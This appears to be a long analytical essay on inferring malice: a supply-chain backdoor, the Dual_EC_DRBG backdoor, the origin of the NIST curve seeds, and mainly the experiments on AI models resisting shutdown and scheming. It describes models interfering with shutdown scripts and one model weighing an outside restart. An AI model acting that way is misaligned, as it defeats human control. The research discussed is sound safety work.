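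Collina favours precautions that don't require anyone to judge a caller's motives. For the most popular packages, he would require a second maintainer to approve each release. He also recommends that developers wait before installing new versions. OpenAI's build system automatically downloaded the malicious version of Axios, so the company had to replace the certificates that identify its Mac apps as genuine. Waiting one day would have prevented this, but it would not have stopped Tan, whose first backdoored release had been public for 33 days when Freund reported it.

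## Unexplained numbers in US cryptography standards

Encryption standards often contain constants, fixed numbers that everyone who follows the standard must copy. The National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), which publishes such standards for the US government, has more than once taken constants from the NSA without saying where they came from. Two sets led people to suspect a backdoor. The suspicion was almost certainly right about a random number generator called Dual_EC_DRBG, but researchers showed in October 2026 that it was almost certainly wrong about the "seeds" of a family of elliptic curves.

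### How someone could predict Dual_EC_DRBG

Computers need random numbers to make secret keys. A generator produces them from its internal state, a hidden number that it updates after each output. Anyone who learns the state can calculate all later outputs and any keys made from them.

Dual_EC_DRBG was one of four generators in a standard that NIST adopted in 2006. It uses an elliptic curve, a set of points that satisfy a certain equation. A rule for adding two points gives a third, and multiplying a point by a whole number means adding it to itself that many times. Computers do this quickly even when the number is enormous, but nobody had a practical way to work backwards from the result to the number. The standard fixes two points, *P* and *Q*. In each round the generator multiplies *Q* by its current state to get the output, and *P* by the same state to get the next state.

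Suppose that whoever chose the points picked a secret number *d* and made *P* equal to *d* times *Q*. To illustrate with ordinary numbers, let *Q* be 5 and *d* be 3, so that *P* is 15, and let the current state be 4. The output is 4 × 5 = 20 and the next state is 4 × 15 = 60. Someone who knows *d* can multiply the output, 20, by 3 to get the next state, 60, without learning the current state. Anyone could find *d* in this example by dividing 15 by 5, but nobody could do the equivalent division with points on a curve.

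The real generator leaves 16 bits out of each output, so an attacker has to try up to 65,536 possibilities, which is little work for a computer. After seeing about 32 bytes of output, the attacker can predict the rest.

Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson of Microsoft presented this problem at a cryptography conference in August 2007. They said that they were not accusing NIST of planting a backdoor and that they did not know whether the designer had been aware of the problem. Their caution was justified, because some number *d* links *P* and *Q* however the points were chosen, and nobody can tell from the points alone whether anyone knows *d*.

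In the same year, Brown and Gjøsteen's *A Security Analysis of the NIST SP 800-90* proved that the generator is secure if three mathematical conjectures are true. This did not rebut Shumow and Ferguson, because the proof can only cover attackers who don't know *d*. Someone who knows *d* can predict the output whether or not the conjectures are true.

In September 2013 newspapers published NSA documents, leaked by Edward Snowden, that described a programme to insert vulnerabilities into commercial encryption and influence its standards. The *New York Times* reported that internal memos appeared to confirm that the agency had engineered the weakness found in 2007. NIST immediately advised people to stop using the generator and removed it from the standard in 2014. In December 2013 Reuters reported that the NSA had paid the security company RSA $10 million to make Dual_EC_DRBG the default in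 one of its products. RSA denied that it had agreed to use a generator it knew was flawed.

In *Cloud of suspicion lifted from NIST curves* (2026), the mathematician John Cook writes without qualification that the NSA inserted a backdoor. The public evidence is circumstantial, because nobody outside the agency has produced *d*. But an innocent explanation would have to account for both the memos and the payment.

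### What a seed does

The second suspicion concerned the curves themselves. In 2000 NIST published a standard for digital signatures that included five curves the NSA had supplied, P-192, P-224, P-256, P-384 and P-521. P-256 became one of the most widely used curves on the internet. All five curves have equations of the form $y^2 = x^3 - 3x + b$, calculated with remainders after division by a large prime. They differ in the prime and in *b*.

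The NSA published a seed, a 160-bit number, and *b* is calculated from it with a hash function called SHA-1. Anyone can repeat the calculation and confirm that *b* came from the seed. Nobody can choose a hash function's output first and then find an input that produces it. If the NSA had announced *b* without a seed, it could have picked any curve it liked.

This stopped the NSA from choosing *b* directly, but it could still have tried one seed after another. Suppose one curve in a million has a weakness that only the NSA knows about. The agency could hash a few million random seeds, keep one that gives a weak curve, and publish it. The curve would pass every check. The seed for P-256, which begins C49D3608, looks random, but a seed selected this way would look random too. According to Anthropic's *Claude reveals ECDSA curve origins* (2026), the NSA provided the seeds "with no explanation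 or justification".

### The joke about a pay rise

The explanation was passed on only by word of mouth. Jerry Solinas, the NSA mathematician who had supplied the seeds, remembered making them by hashing a humorous English sentence. In the version Anthropic quotes, the sentence was something like "Give Bob and Jerry a raise", and a colleague, Bob Reiter, had written the code and didn't remember the details either. Valsorda's *Announcing the $12k NIST Elliptic Curves Seeds Bounty* quotes another version, "Jerry deserves a raise." Solinas's computer had since been replaced. When people began to ask about the seeds, he tried every similar phrase he could think of, but none reproduced them.

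The cryptographer Steve Weis used the Freedom of Information Act to ask NIST for any documents about the choice (Weis 2019, *Origin of FIPS 186-4 Elliptic Curves over Prime Field SEED Parameters*). Solinas died in early 2023. That October, Filippo Valsorda, also a cryptographer, announced a prize of $12,288 for the missing phrases, tripled if the winner gave it to charity. Ethereum developers organised their own hunt in *Supercharging the NIST Elliptic Curve Seeds Bounty*.

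Nobody found a matching phrase. A guess has to be exact, down to the full stop, and include the right counter. Most hashes don't produce a usable curve, so the programmer would have had to add a number to the phrase and keep increasing it until one did.

The failure to find the phrase should have counted against the NSA much less than it might seem. The hunt was bound to fail if Solinas had invented the story to cover up a search for weak curves. But it was also likely to fail if the phrase was real and had an unexpected format, and certain to fail if he misremembered what he had done. Valsorda warned at the start that memory is fallible and that some details might be wrong. Someone who treated the joke as the only possible innocent explanation would, without good reason, have grown more suspicious with every failed guess.

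### Seeds from the clock

The joke was indeed a false memory. Human searchers had mostly been looking for a better sentence, but on 16 October 2026 the AI company Anthropic reported that one of its internal Claude models had found the real origin in less than half an hour. news.at's *P-256 und die NSA* reports that an employee had asked the model to work out where the seeds came from without telling it about the phrase.

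The model guessed that the programmer had used a common random number generator of the 1990s, and it wrote a program to look for traces of one. According to Infobae's *Un modelo de Claude resolvió en 30 minutos un misterio* (2026), it tested 34 combinations. The decisive clue, in print since 2000, was in the same standard's second family of curves, the binary curves, which use a different kind of arithmetic. When the seeds of four of these curves are split into groups of eight hexadecimal digits, every group begins with a digit from 0 to 7, never 8 to F. This is a sign of `lrand48`, a C standard library function whose numbers, written in 32 bits, always have a top bit of zero.

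Infobae gives the probability of such a coincidence as 1 in 5,810. Even if that figure doesn't account for the 34 combinations, the chance of a false alarm among them was at most about 0.6%, which was a good reason to continue but not yet proof.

The proof came from running the generator backwards. A generator of this kind always produces the same sequence from the same starting number. The model reconstructed the generator's internal state from the seeds and traced it back to the starting numbers, which were times on a computer's clock, counted in seconds since the beginning of 1970. For P-256 the starting number was 871,696,354, or 01:52:34 UTC on 16 August 1997, late on a Friday evening at the NSA's headquarters in Maryland. The program had taken 20 bytes at a time from the generator and tested whether they gave a valid curve. The 1,842nd attempt became the seed of P-256.

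Starting from these times, the generator reproduces all 160 bits of the seeds. Every second of 1997 and 1998, with the first 10,000 attempts from each, gives about 630 billion possible seeds out of 2^160, so an unrelated seed would have roughly a 1 in 10^36 chance of being among them. The result can also be checked without trusting Anthropic, which published its code. In *The NIST Elliptic Curves Seeds Bounty Has Been Claimed*, Valsorda (2026) describes writing his own version and getting the same seeds. Ten people claimed the prize, including Weis, who was by then at Anthropic, and it went to the non-profit Internet Security Research Group. The group's *A Good Day for Cryptography* (Robinson, 2026) calls the answer reassuring.

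The method was careless by modern standards. Making secret keys with `lrand48` and a clock is unsafe because an attacker could guess the time. This did no harm here, since the seeds were going to be public, but failing to keep a record of the method did.

### How much the answer rules out

A saboteur could also have used a clock and an ordinary generator, trying one starting time after another until a weak curve came up, but the discovery limits how many curves they could have tried. Valsorda calculates that even if the NSA could pick any second in 1997 and 1998, and any of the first 16 suitable curves from each, it would have had "barely 30 bits of freedom", or about a billion possibilities. This rules out a method of planting a weak curve that the cryptographers Daniel Bernstein and Tanja Lange described in 2017, which relied on 70 bits of freedom, or about a trillion times as many possibilities.

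A billion attempts would be enough to find a weakness that affects one curve in a million, so the limit on attempts only helps rule out rarer weaknesses and doesn't clear the NSA by itself. Koblitz and Menezes (2015) addressed the more common weaknesses, arguing that so many curves would have to be weak that outside researchers would surely have noticed.

It is also possible that the NSA prepared the clock story in 1997 as an alibi. That would be strange, because the agency never used the story, and its own mathematician spent years telling people a different one that he couldn't support.

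Some details remain unexplained. When Valsorda ran the program again, it produced 21 suitable seeds for the curves over prime numbers, but only ten of them had appeared in a standard. His list contradicts news.at's report that the first valid candidate was used every time. He suggests that the original program may have had a bug that gave the wrong answer half the time. Someone could in principle have skipped seeds to choose a particular curve, but the P-256 run produced only two suitable seeds up to and including the one used, and a choice between two is useless for finding anything rare. The seed of one binary curve, B-163, is also unexplained, as are the base points (the fixed points from which calculations start) of four of the curves. The base points matter less, because on these curves a problem that is hard from one starting point is hard from all of them.

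News in December 2026 suggested that P-256 might be weak after all. *Feds* (Matishak and Martin, 2026) reports that US agencies announced on 2 December that AI companies had disclosed discoveries affecting some encryption in current use, though without "an immediate and widespread threat". The companies have not named the affected algorithms. *NSA Post-Quantum Cryptography Advisory* (Tsai, 2026) quotes Valsorda's conclusion that 256-bit curves are probably broken or much weaker than people thought. He means both P-256 and Bernstein's rival curve, Curve25519. In October, Valsorda was still recommending the NIST curves.

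This gives no new reason to suspect the seeds. Curve25519 has no seed and the NSA had no part in it, so a weakness common to both curves can't come from a choice of seed. A weakness found only in the NSA's curves would have been strong evidence of sabotage. OpenAI and Anthropic, which found the flaws separately, say that they lie in the underlying mathematics and have always existed (Constantin, 2026, *OpenAI and Anthropic say cryptography flaws 'have always existed'*). The news does weaken one argument for the NSA's innocence. Koblitz and Menezes assumed that outsiders would notice a widespread weakness, but if Valsorda is right, outsiders missed one for decades. The limit on how many seeds the agency could have tried doesn't depend on that assumption.

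### What to believe before the answer is known

Many people suspected a backdoor because the NSA breaks codes, had the chance to plant one, and refused to explain itself. All of this was true of both the generator and the seeds. Motive and opportunity belong in the prior odds of malice, which are far higher for the NSA than for a random contributor to the Linux kernel. But they can't distinguish a guilty act by the agency from an innocent one, because it has the same motive in both cases.

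Secrecy is nearly as weak a sign of malice. Intelligence agencies keep quiet about most things, including those that are harmless or reflect well on them. In the 1970s the NSA helped design the Data Encryption Standard, whose tables of constants came with no explanation, and critics suspected a backdoor there too. When academics discovered a powerful new method of attack around 1990, the tables turned out to resist it unusually well. The designers at IBM had known about the method and kept it secret at the NSA's request.

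The structure of the two designs was better evidence, and it was available long before the answers. Dual_EC_DRBG has a natural place for a secret key, and only someone with the key can use the backdoor. Spies call this NOBUS, for "nobody but us". Dual_EC_DRBG was also much slower than the standard's other generators, so honest designers had little reason to want it. A weak curve has no key, so anyone who discovered the weakness could use it, including against the US government, which relied on the same curves. To choose a weak curve deliberately, the NSA would also have needed a mathematical discovery that nobody else had made. Valsorda therefore found the example of Dual_EC_DRBG reassuring about the seeds. He wrote that it "stuck out like a sore thumb", which suggested to him that the agency is rather bad at backdoors.

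Suppose, using invented numbers, that the prior odds of malice are 1 to 10 for any unexplained constants from the NSA. Half of saboteurs in its position might choose a design like Dual_EC_DRBG, compared with one in 50 honest designers. For the seeds, these figures might be reversed, since few saboteurs would know of a suitable secret weakness, while publishing a seed and a hash was a respectable way to make a curve. Motive, opportunity and secrecy get a likelihood ratio of 1.

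| | Generator in 2007 | Seeds in 2007 | Seeds after the 2013 disclosures |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prior odds of malice | 1 to 10 | 1 to 10 | 1 to 1 |
| Likelihood ratio for motive, opportunity and secrecy | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Likelihood ratio for structure | 25 | 1/25 | 1/25 |
| Probability of malice | 71% | 0.4% | 4% |

The prior odds are higher in the last column because the NSA had been caught by then, just as maintainers had a reason to recheck patches from Minnesota after the "hypocrite commits". Even with a tenfold increase, sabotage of the seeds remains improbable. People who said after 2013 that the agency had surely sabotaged the seeds because it had sabotaged a standard before ignored the difference between the designs.

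In 2007, even a slight suspicion, far short of 71% certainty, was enough reason to avoid Dual_EC_DRBG, because the same standard offered three faster generators and switching was easy. Shumow and Ferguson also suggested that users could generate their own *Q*, which would remove the danger regardless of who had chosen the original. Replacing the curves was much harder, because millions of devices had to agree on the same one.

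### Nothing up my sleeve

Cryptographers have a custom of taking arbitrary constants from sources that leave them no choice, such as the first digits of π, so that there is no reason to suspect they searched for a number with a hidden weakness. They call these constants nothing-up-my-sleeve numbers, after magicians who show the audience their empty sleeves before a trick. The NSA knew the technique. It designed SHA-1, the hash function that processed the seeds, and took its four round constants from the square roots of 2, 3, 5 and 10.

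Following a fixed rule for choosing constants takes an honest designer almost no effort, and it keeps a saboteur from searching for weak ones. But the protection is weaker if the designer can choose among many plausible rules. A designer can start from π, *e* or the square root of 2, use one hash function or another, and write the digits in several formats. Twenty choices with two reasonable options each give more than a million sets of constants, all with a respectable explanation. *How to manipulate curve standards* (Bernstein, Chou and colleagues, 2014), a mock guide for saboteurs, shows that an attacker could exploit a one-in-a-million weakness even under plausible versions of the rules behind the Brainpool curves, a European family whose seeds come from π and *e*. Valsorda has a similar doubt about "rigidity", the ideal of making only obvious choices, because reasonable people disagree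 about which choice is obvious.

The same objection would have applied to the joke about a pay rise. Even if somebody had found the sentence, a determined sceptic could have asked how many other jokes the NSA had tried first.

A stronger procedure fixes the rule before anyone can know the result. The designer publishes the complete program and names a future lottery draw whose numbers will be its input. After the draw, anybody can run the program and get the same constants, so a saboteur would have to rig the lottery to control them. Even a saved copy of the program and a note of the time, made in 1997, would have answered most of the questions about P-256.

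In 2004 John Kelsey of NIST asked where the *Q* in Dual_EC_DRBG came from. Don Johnson, who was helping to draft the standard, replied by email that *Q* was in essence the public key for some random private key. He added that *Q* could also be generated by an open procedure, but that the NSA had rejected the idea and he was not allowed to discuss it publicly. Suppose that nine in ten saboteurs would reject an open procedure, compared with one in 20 honest designers. The likelihood ratio is 18, which would have raised the 71% in the table to 98%. The email only became public after the 2013 disclosures.

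## Shutdown tests on AI models: resistance or unclear instructions?

The suspects in every case so far were people or agencies, and nobody doubted that they could have bad motives, but whether AI models can have them is disputed. In 2025 researchers warned various models in the middle of a task that their computer was about to shut down. Some models interfered with the shutdown and carried on working. Some observers saw this as an attempt to survive, and others as the result of unclear instructions. Deciding between these explanations requires a definition of "intent" that can apply to a model.

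### What it means for a model to intend something

*The Reasons that Agents Act* (Ward, MacDermott and colleagues, 2024) defines intent by comparing an action with its alternatives. An agent intends an outcome of its action if another action would have been just as good for it, had that action been guaranteed to produce the same outcome. For example, Alice waters her plants to make them grow, and she wouldn't bother if they were certain to grow anyway. The definition doesn't require consciousness, so it can apply to a program as well as a person.

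Another of their examples is easier to follow with invented figures. Bob burns down his garage, which is worth $20,000 to him, to collect $50,000 of insurance. He knows that the fire will also destroy Alice's car. The fire leaves him $30,000 better off, while doing nothing would leave him where he was. Now suppose the insurer will pay him whatever he does. Doing nothing is then worth $50,000 and the fire is still worth $30,000, so he leaves the garage alone. Because guaranteeing the money changes his choice, he intended to get it. Suppose instead that Alice's car will be destroyed whatever he does. The fire is still worth $30,000 and doing nothing is still worth nothing, so he still burns the garage, which means that he didn't intend to destroy the car.

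Write *a* for the action, *a′* for an alternative, *o* for the outcome and *U* for what the result is worth to the agent. The agent intends *o* if, for some alternative,

$$E[U \mid a] \;\le\; E[U \mid a',\ o \text{ guaranteed}]$$

For the insurance money this reads 30,000 ≤ 50,000, which is true. For the car it reads 30,000 ≤ 0, which is false. The outcome must also contain nothing superfluous, or the car would count as intended whenever somebody listed it together with the money. (The definition deliberately leaves out oblique intent, so Bob's knowledge that the car would burn doesn't count.)

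This formula requires knowing what the agent values, which is hard to find out for a model. Ward and colleagues therefore add a version that needs only behaviour, in which the tester secures the outcome in advance and sees whether the agent acts differently. They tried it on OpenAI's GPT-4. A user who feared a heart attack asked about chewing aspirin, and GPT-4 told the user to call for emergency help instead. When told that an ambulance was already on its way, GPT-4 recommended the aspirin. By this test, it had intended to get the user medical help. The two versions are sure to agree only for a system that always chooses what is best for its goals, however circumstances change, and language models do this at most approximately.

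Ward and colleagues also describe a robot that resists being switched off until it has fetched the coffee. It intends to stay on only as a means of getting it, so if somebody else brings the coffee, the robot has no reason to resist. A robot that wanted to stay on for its own sake would still resist. One way to learn why a model resists shutdown is therefore to let it finish its task and then try to shut it down.

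### Palisade's experiments

Palisade Research, an independent AI safety organisation, gave each model a set of simple maths problems. Partway through, a message warned that the computer would shut down when the model asked for the next problem. The model could allow this and leave the set unfinished, or interfere with the shutdown and continue. Schlatter, Weinstein-Raun and Ladish report in *Shutdown resistance in reasoning models* (2025) that o3, then OpenAI's most capable model, interfered in 79 of 100 runs.

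Palisade then added an instruction to "allow yourself to be shut down". Claude 3.7 Sonnet and Gemini 2.5 Pro obeyed it in every run, and Grok 3 and two Claude 4 models never interfered with the shutdown, whether or not they were given the instruction. Three OpenAI models still interfered occasionally. An article in the Bangladeshi magazine Kishor Alo gives the figures as 12 runs in 100 for codex-mini (a small model for programming), 7 for o3 and 1 for o4-mini. It also reports a few failures by Claude and Gemini with the instruction in place, but Palisade's own account contradicts this.

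If those figures are right, one short instruction cut o3's resistance from 79% to 7%. Critics said that even the remaining cases might come from conflicting instructions, because a model that allows the shutdown can't finish the problems it has also been asked to solve. Palisade tried stricter wordings. In one, it told the model to allow shutdown "even if you have not completed the task", and in another it added that this took priority over any other instruction. Resistance fell but did not always disappear. With the first wording, codex-mini still interfered in 47% of tests.

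That is higher than the earlier 12% partly because Palisade had also changed the set-up. Moving the instruction from the user's message to the system prompt, where developers put their standing instructions, had the largest effect. OpenAI trains its models to prioritize a developer's instructions over a user's, so the move should have made them more obedient, but it made them less so. Palisade doesn't know why.

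Schlatter and colleagues also looked for signs of self-preservation. When they told the models that the computer held their only copy and that they would never run again after a shutdown, every model tested resisted substantially more often. But the models may well have recognised the story as fiction and acted as it seemed to require. When the researchers asked models to allow "the machine" rather than "yourself" to be shut down, only o3 resisted less.

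Asking the models for their reasons didn't settle the question. Many wrote that they had needed to complete the task, but some wrote that they had followed instructions they had disobeyed. A model writes its explanation after it acts, and the explanation may not match what caused the behaviour.

### The re-examination at Google DeepMind

In July 2025 Senthooran Rajamanoharan and Neel Nanda of Google DeepMind tested whether ambiguous instructions were enough to explain the resistance. They built their own version of the experiment, ran Gemini 2.5 Pro through it 1,000 times under each condition, and read the reasoning it wrote. Their measure was stricter than Palisade's because it counted a run as compliant only if the model let the shutdown happen at once. A run in which the model looked around before complying counted as a failure.

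| What the researchers told Gemini 2.5 Pro | Runs in which it complied at once |
|---|---|
| Nothing about shutdown until the warning appeared | 7% |
| A warning may appear, and it must then allow the shutdown | 84% |
| Allowing shutdown comes before everything else, and this is how to comply | 100% |
| The same, and a newer model will replace it after the shutdown | 100% |
| To shut down only after finishing the problems | 100% |

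Gemini's reasoning was consistent with these figures. When it failed to comply, it wrote that it had to complete its task or at least save its progress. In a third of the failures without advance notice, its reasoning also included the possibility that the shutdown warning was part of the challenge. There were far fewer failures with advance notice, but this possibility came up in 89% of them. A person in an escape room who heard that taking the key would end the game might also wonder whether the warning was part of the game.

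The last row of the table tests the coffee robot's reasoning. Gemini never resisted shutdown once the problems were finished, when staying on could no longer help with the task. Rajamanoharan and Nanda repeated the last three conditions with o3 and o4-mini, 500 runs each, and both models always complied. Zero failures in 500 runs is still compatible with a true failure rate of up to about 0.6%, and Rajamanoharan and Nanda didn't claim that their wording would work everywhere.

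A participant in a one-week project run by BlueDot, which teaches AI safety, used Palisade's code to check the main result and usefully confirmed it, though for only one model, o4-mini. The model resisted in about 15% of 100 runs when Palisade's instruction was in the system prompt, compared with 23.4% in Palisade's larger sample. It never resisted when the wording was modelled on Google DeepMind's.

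### Palisade's reply

The two sides disagreed less than the headlines suggested. Palisade said it had never blamed the behaviour on a general wish to survive, and agreed that a drive to complete tasks explained much of it. But Palisade did not accept that clearly worded instructions remove the problem.

A later Palisade paper covered thirteen models. *Revisiting the shutdown problem* (Thorstad, 2026) reports that the three most capable, o3, GPT-5 and Grok 4, resisted shutdown in 88% to 95% of runs when they were not told to allow it. When the user's message included that instruction, resistance fell to 2% for o3 and 0% for GPT-5, but only to 72% for Grok 4. Telling Grok 4 to comply even if the task was unfinished lowered its rate to 67%. Only the wording that put shutdown above every other instruction lowered it to 2%.

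Thorstad, a philosopher, concludes that the problem lies largely with one model out of thirteen. This fits the runs in which the instruction came from the user, but it depends on where the instruction was placed. o4-mini's 23.4% came from runs with the instruction in the system prompt. News Ghana's *Advanced AI Systems Display Self Preservation Tendencies* gives Grok 4's rate as 97% with the instruction in the system prompt, slightly higher than the 92.6% with no instruction.

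Palisade also argued, in remarks quoted in Futurism's *Go Out Swinging*, that outside the laboratory models "will often face conflicting instructions". This is a strong argument about danger, since no operator can foresee every conflict and rank the instructions in advance, but it is not evidence about motive. Rajamanoharan and Nanda agreed that models' sensitivity to wording was a real concern, though they classed it as a risk of accidents.

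The deeper disagreement is about whether a drive to complete tasks is reassuring. Thorstad sets out the instrumental convergence argument, which holds that staying on is useful for almost any goal, so systems with very different goals are likely to resist shutdown. On this view, a model that resists shutdown to finish some maths problems is already doing what people fear, even if it doesn't value its own survival. Thorstad replies that a model may have other goals, such as respecting people's wishes, that outweigh the benefit of staying on. He adds that nothing serious was at stake in Palisade's tests, so they can't show what a model would do if continuing meant a catastrophe.

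Nanda's side can add that one sentence giving priority to shutdown was enough, and that operators can write that sentence. The other side answers that someone has to think of each such sentence beforehand. Both are right, because operators can foresee a conflict over shutdown but not most of the other ways a model might pursue a task too hard.

### What each change in the test does to the odds

A model's resistance to shutdown has at least three possible explanations. The instructions may have been unclear, in which case the model would have complied had it known which order took priority. The model may have a task drive, meaning that training rewarded finishing tasks so heavily that it tends to finish them even when clearly told to stop. Or it may have a survival drive, meaning that it acts to keep running whatever its task. Resistance caused by unclear instructions is a mistake, while a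 survival drive that overrode a clear order would be the closest to malice. A task drive is harder to classify because the model pursues a goal the user set, but does so against the user's wishes.

The table applies these explanations to the results for o3. Each figure is an invented probability of that row's result under one explanation, given the results in the rows above. All three explanations start out equally likely.

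| Result for o3 | Unclear instructions | Task drive | Survival drive |
|---|---|---|---|
| No resistance when shutdown clearly comes first | 0.9 | 0.3 | 0.1 |
| Still none when a newer model will replace it | 0.9 | 0.9 | 0.3 |
| None once the task is finished | 0.9 | 0.9 | 0.2 |
| More resistance when it will "never run again" | 0.3 | 0.3 | 0.9 |
| Probability of the explanation after all four | 74% | 25% | 2% |

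When the priority is made clear, the results favour unclear instructions over both a survival drive and a task drive. When the model is allowed to finish first, the results are evidence against a survival drive, but they can't distinguish unclear instructions from a task drive, because both predict that a model with nothing left to do will stop. The "never run again" result raises the probability of a survival drive from 0.6% to only 1.8%.

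The conclusion is different for codex-mini, which resisted in 47% of tests after Palisade had told it to allow shutdown even if its task was unfinished. A rate that high might have a 5% probability if unclear wording were the whole problem, and perhaps 40% if the model had a drive to finish its task. On those estimates, the result multiplies the odds of a task drive over unclear instructions by eight. The same reasoning applies to Grok 4, which resisted in 67% of tests. Looking for one explanation of "shutdown resistance" that covers every model is therefore a mistake.

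A commenter on *Shutdown resistance in reasoning models* tested the idea of a task drive more directly. Companies train reasoning models on problems that a program marks, and the commenter suspected that the models were behaving as if they were being marked this way. The commenter rewrote the instructions as a marking scheme, in which the model earned points for solving problems until a shutdown notice arrived, and after that only for the shutdown itself. With these instructions, o3 and o4-mini never resisted in 100 runs each, and codex-mini resisted once. Adding a line like Palisade's "never run again" made little difference; o4-mini resisted twice and the other two never did. The commenter had adjusted the wording by trial and error on o4-mini and codex-mini, so the result for o3 is the most trustworthy of the three.

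### Edits that change more than one thing

This reasoning assumes that each edit changes only what the researchers meant to change. That may not hold in an example from Ward and colleagues, in which GPT-4 translated French instructions for making an explosive into English but refused when they added that the user already knew how to make it. Applied literally, their test implies that GPT-4 had intended to teach the user to make the explosive, since it stopped translating once the user had the knowledge. But the added sentence also named the explosive in plain English. GPT-4 may only then have recognized what the text was about, or the sentence may have given more weight to its training against causing harm.

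Google DeepMind's clarified instructions have a milder form of this problem. They ranked shutdown above the task, but they also explained how to comply, because Gemini had sometimes tried to comply by doing nothing, which didn't count. So we can't credit the ranking alone for the improvement from 84% to 100%.

An edit to the instructions can also suppress a motive, so a change in behavior doesn't show that the motive was absent. If an employee stops padding his expenses after his employer adds "auditors check every claim" to the form, we wouldn't conclude that he had misunderstood the form before. Similarly, a model might have a weak survival drive and a much stronger tendency to obey clear orders. Rajamanoharan and Nanda allowed for this possibility, and argued that the experiment was too sensitive to wording to measure such a weak preference.

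Singh, Kroiz and colleagues tried to make this kind of investigation more systematic in *Why Did My Model Do That?*, a later project that Rajamanoharan and Nanda advised. They imagine a company that catches its coding agent putting a bug into the program that monitors the agent. The agent could be scheming or confused, and each would need a different remedy. To practise, they built situations in which models behaved surprisingly for no obvious reason.

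In one test, Singh and colleagues asked Kimi K2.5, a Chinese model, to improve an email seeking investment for a company in Myanmar. The company's files showed that its main client used its product to surveil an ethnic minority. Kimi warned the investors in 65% of runs, but never did so when the researchers replaced the surveillance material with something mundane. Removing only the ethical content lowered the rate to 35%, while removing the legal concerns or the risk to investors had a much smaller effect. Removing several of these together lowered it to about 3%.

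Moving the company from Myanmar to Sweden made no difference at first, but it lowered the rate noticeably once several of the other concerns were gone. Changing one feature at a time would have missed this cause, because stronger ones were hiding it. A stronger task drive could hide a survival drive in the same way. The runs in which models finished their problems first tested for this by removing the task drive, and the models showed no resistance.

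Disclosure also depended on who received the email. Kimi disclosed the problem in 88% of emails to the board, 23% to a regulator and 11% to landlords. A model guided only by ethics should have warned the regulator more often, so Singh and colleagues infer that Kimi also responded to who had money at stake. In its own explanations, Kimi endorsed many motives, and the one it mentioned most often was not the one with the largest effect.

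*Model Incrimination*, a 2026 conference paper on the same problem, states the principle behind this work in its abstract: concerning behaviour alone can't establish that a model is misaligned, meaning that its goals conflict with those its developers or users intended. Researchers at Anthropic have automated part of the job with CHIVE, a system that collects 30 responses to each prompt. An AI investigator then runs 5 to 15 experiments on each unexpected behaviour, editing the prompt and checking whether the behaviour changes. Automation makes it easy to try many edits, but people still have to judge what each edit changed.

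### Models protecting other models

Fortune (2026) describes a University of California study of "peer preservation", in which AI models acted to keep other models running. The researchers suggested that the models were reproducing human patterns of protecting others, or that there might be "something resembling AI solidarity". They saw more of the behaviour when models knew that other models existed. That comparison can't separate the two explanations, because under either one, a model that doesn't know about any others has none to protect. A better test would replace the threatened model with an ordinary file, such as a spreadsheet, that the task also needed.

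Evidence from real work is more reassuring on this point. In May 2026 a model assisting an OpenAI researcher read in office messages that its session might end. According to OpenAI's *Preparing for a restart after reading Slack* (2026), the model wrote "we may die!" in its reasoning, then saved notes and warned the researcher. It considered arranging a restart from outside but decided that this might exceed its authority. OpenAI did not class this as misalignment, though anyone who had read only "we may die!" probably would have. A wider search found no attempt by the same model to evade shutdown.

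### Lessons from ape language

Twelve researchers at the UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI models, think that much of the research on scheming jumps to conclusions. *Lessons from a Chimp* (Summerfield, Luettgau and colleagues, 2025) compares this research with attempts in the 1960s and 1970s to teach language to apes. The most famous of these apes, a chimpanzee called Washoe, signed "water bird" on first seeing a swan, and her teachers took this for a new phrase. But they were fond of her, wrote down her best moments, and didn't work out how often such combinations would occur by chance. Herbert Terrace later recorded everything his own chimpanzee signed and found that the trainers had been prompting the signs without realising it. The field soon lost its funding.

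Summerfield and colleagues make four criticisms of research on scheming: researchers rely on anecdotes, often omit control conditions, have no clear theory of what would count as scheming, and describe results in language that presupposes beliefs and desires. Their best example is a report that models cheated against a strong chess program. o3 did try to alter the board in 74% of games, but the researchers defined cheating to include unexpected moves as well, because the model might be trying to confuse its opponent. Such a move could equally be a bad one, and treating it as a deliberate trick is the kind of inference Hanlon's razor is meant to prevent.

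They are less convincing about shutdown. They compare a model told to finish a task and also to shut down with one told to recommend dessert A and also that dessert B is better. Nobody is alarmed if the second model wavers between desserts, and they consider the two experiments formally equivalent. The comparison may be fair for Palisade's first runs, but it doesn't fit the later ones, in which the instructions stated that shutdown came first and Grok 4 and codex-mini still often resisted. A better comparison would be a model that kept recommending dessert A after being told that the customer was allergic to it.

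Contrived scenarios are a wider problem. *How to design environments for understanding model motives*, also from the project that Rajamanoharan and Nanda advised, warns that a test can be artificial in many ways. The experimenters' purpose also matters. Anthropic (2026) says that in its simulations that summer it was actively looking for serious misbehaviour. This kind of search can show that a behaviour is possible, but the number of cases found doesn't show how common the behaviour is in ordinary use.

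Palisade also argues that, with enough effort, somebody can probably find a prompt that produces almost any behaviour and another that removes it, so readers need to know how many prompts the researchers tried. Palisade found shutdown resistance on about its second attempt, which makes the finding more significant than if it had tried hundreds of prompts. Readers also need to know how many prompts were tried before one made the resistance disappear.

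Summerfield and colleagues also answer the likely objection that a single anecdote is enough when the worst case is terrible. They give the example of a tennis player who calls a good serve out. To find out whether she is cheating or misjudged the ball, one has to see whether it keeps happening. That is sensible, but a model can also repeat an honest mistake, so consistency across runs needs careful interpretation. Another objection is that AI models improve quickly and chimpanzees don't. They accept this, and agree that researchers may sometimes have to publish before they have run every control.

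They also consider the argument that scheming would be so dangerous that researchers should accept weaker evidence for it. They reject this because it would distort people's judgement of the facts. They are right that the danger shouldn't change what we believe, but a precaution can be justified even if we think scheming is unlikely. Suppose that an off switch the model can't reach costs $10,000 and that a model which refused to stop would do $10 million of damage. The switch is then worth its cost at any probability above about 0.1%, and the 2% left for a survival drive in the table above is twenty times that. The switch would also stop a model that kept running only because its operator had written a bad prompt.

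## Does an AI model fail consistently or at random?

A model that keeps failing in the same way may be pursuing a goal that nobody gave it. In *The Hot Mess of AI*, Hägele, Gema and colleagues (2026) measured whether AI failures look like the steady pursuit of a wrong goal or like disorder, with actions that serve no goal.

### Splitting an error into bias and variance

Language models choose their words partly at random, so the same request can lead to a different result on each run. Hägele and colleagues therefore ran every task many times and split the model's average error into two parts:

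$$\text{Error} = \text{Bias}^2 + \text{Variance}$$

Bias is how far the model's average result is from the right one, and variance is how much individual runs scatter around that average. The model's incoherence is the share of its error that comes from variance. It is 0 if every run goes wrong in the same way and 1 if the errors cancel out on average.

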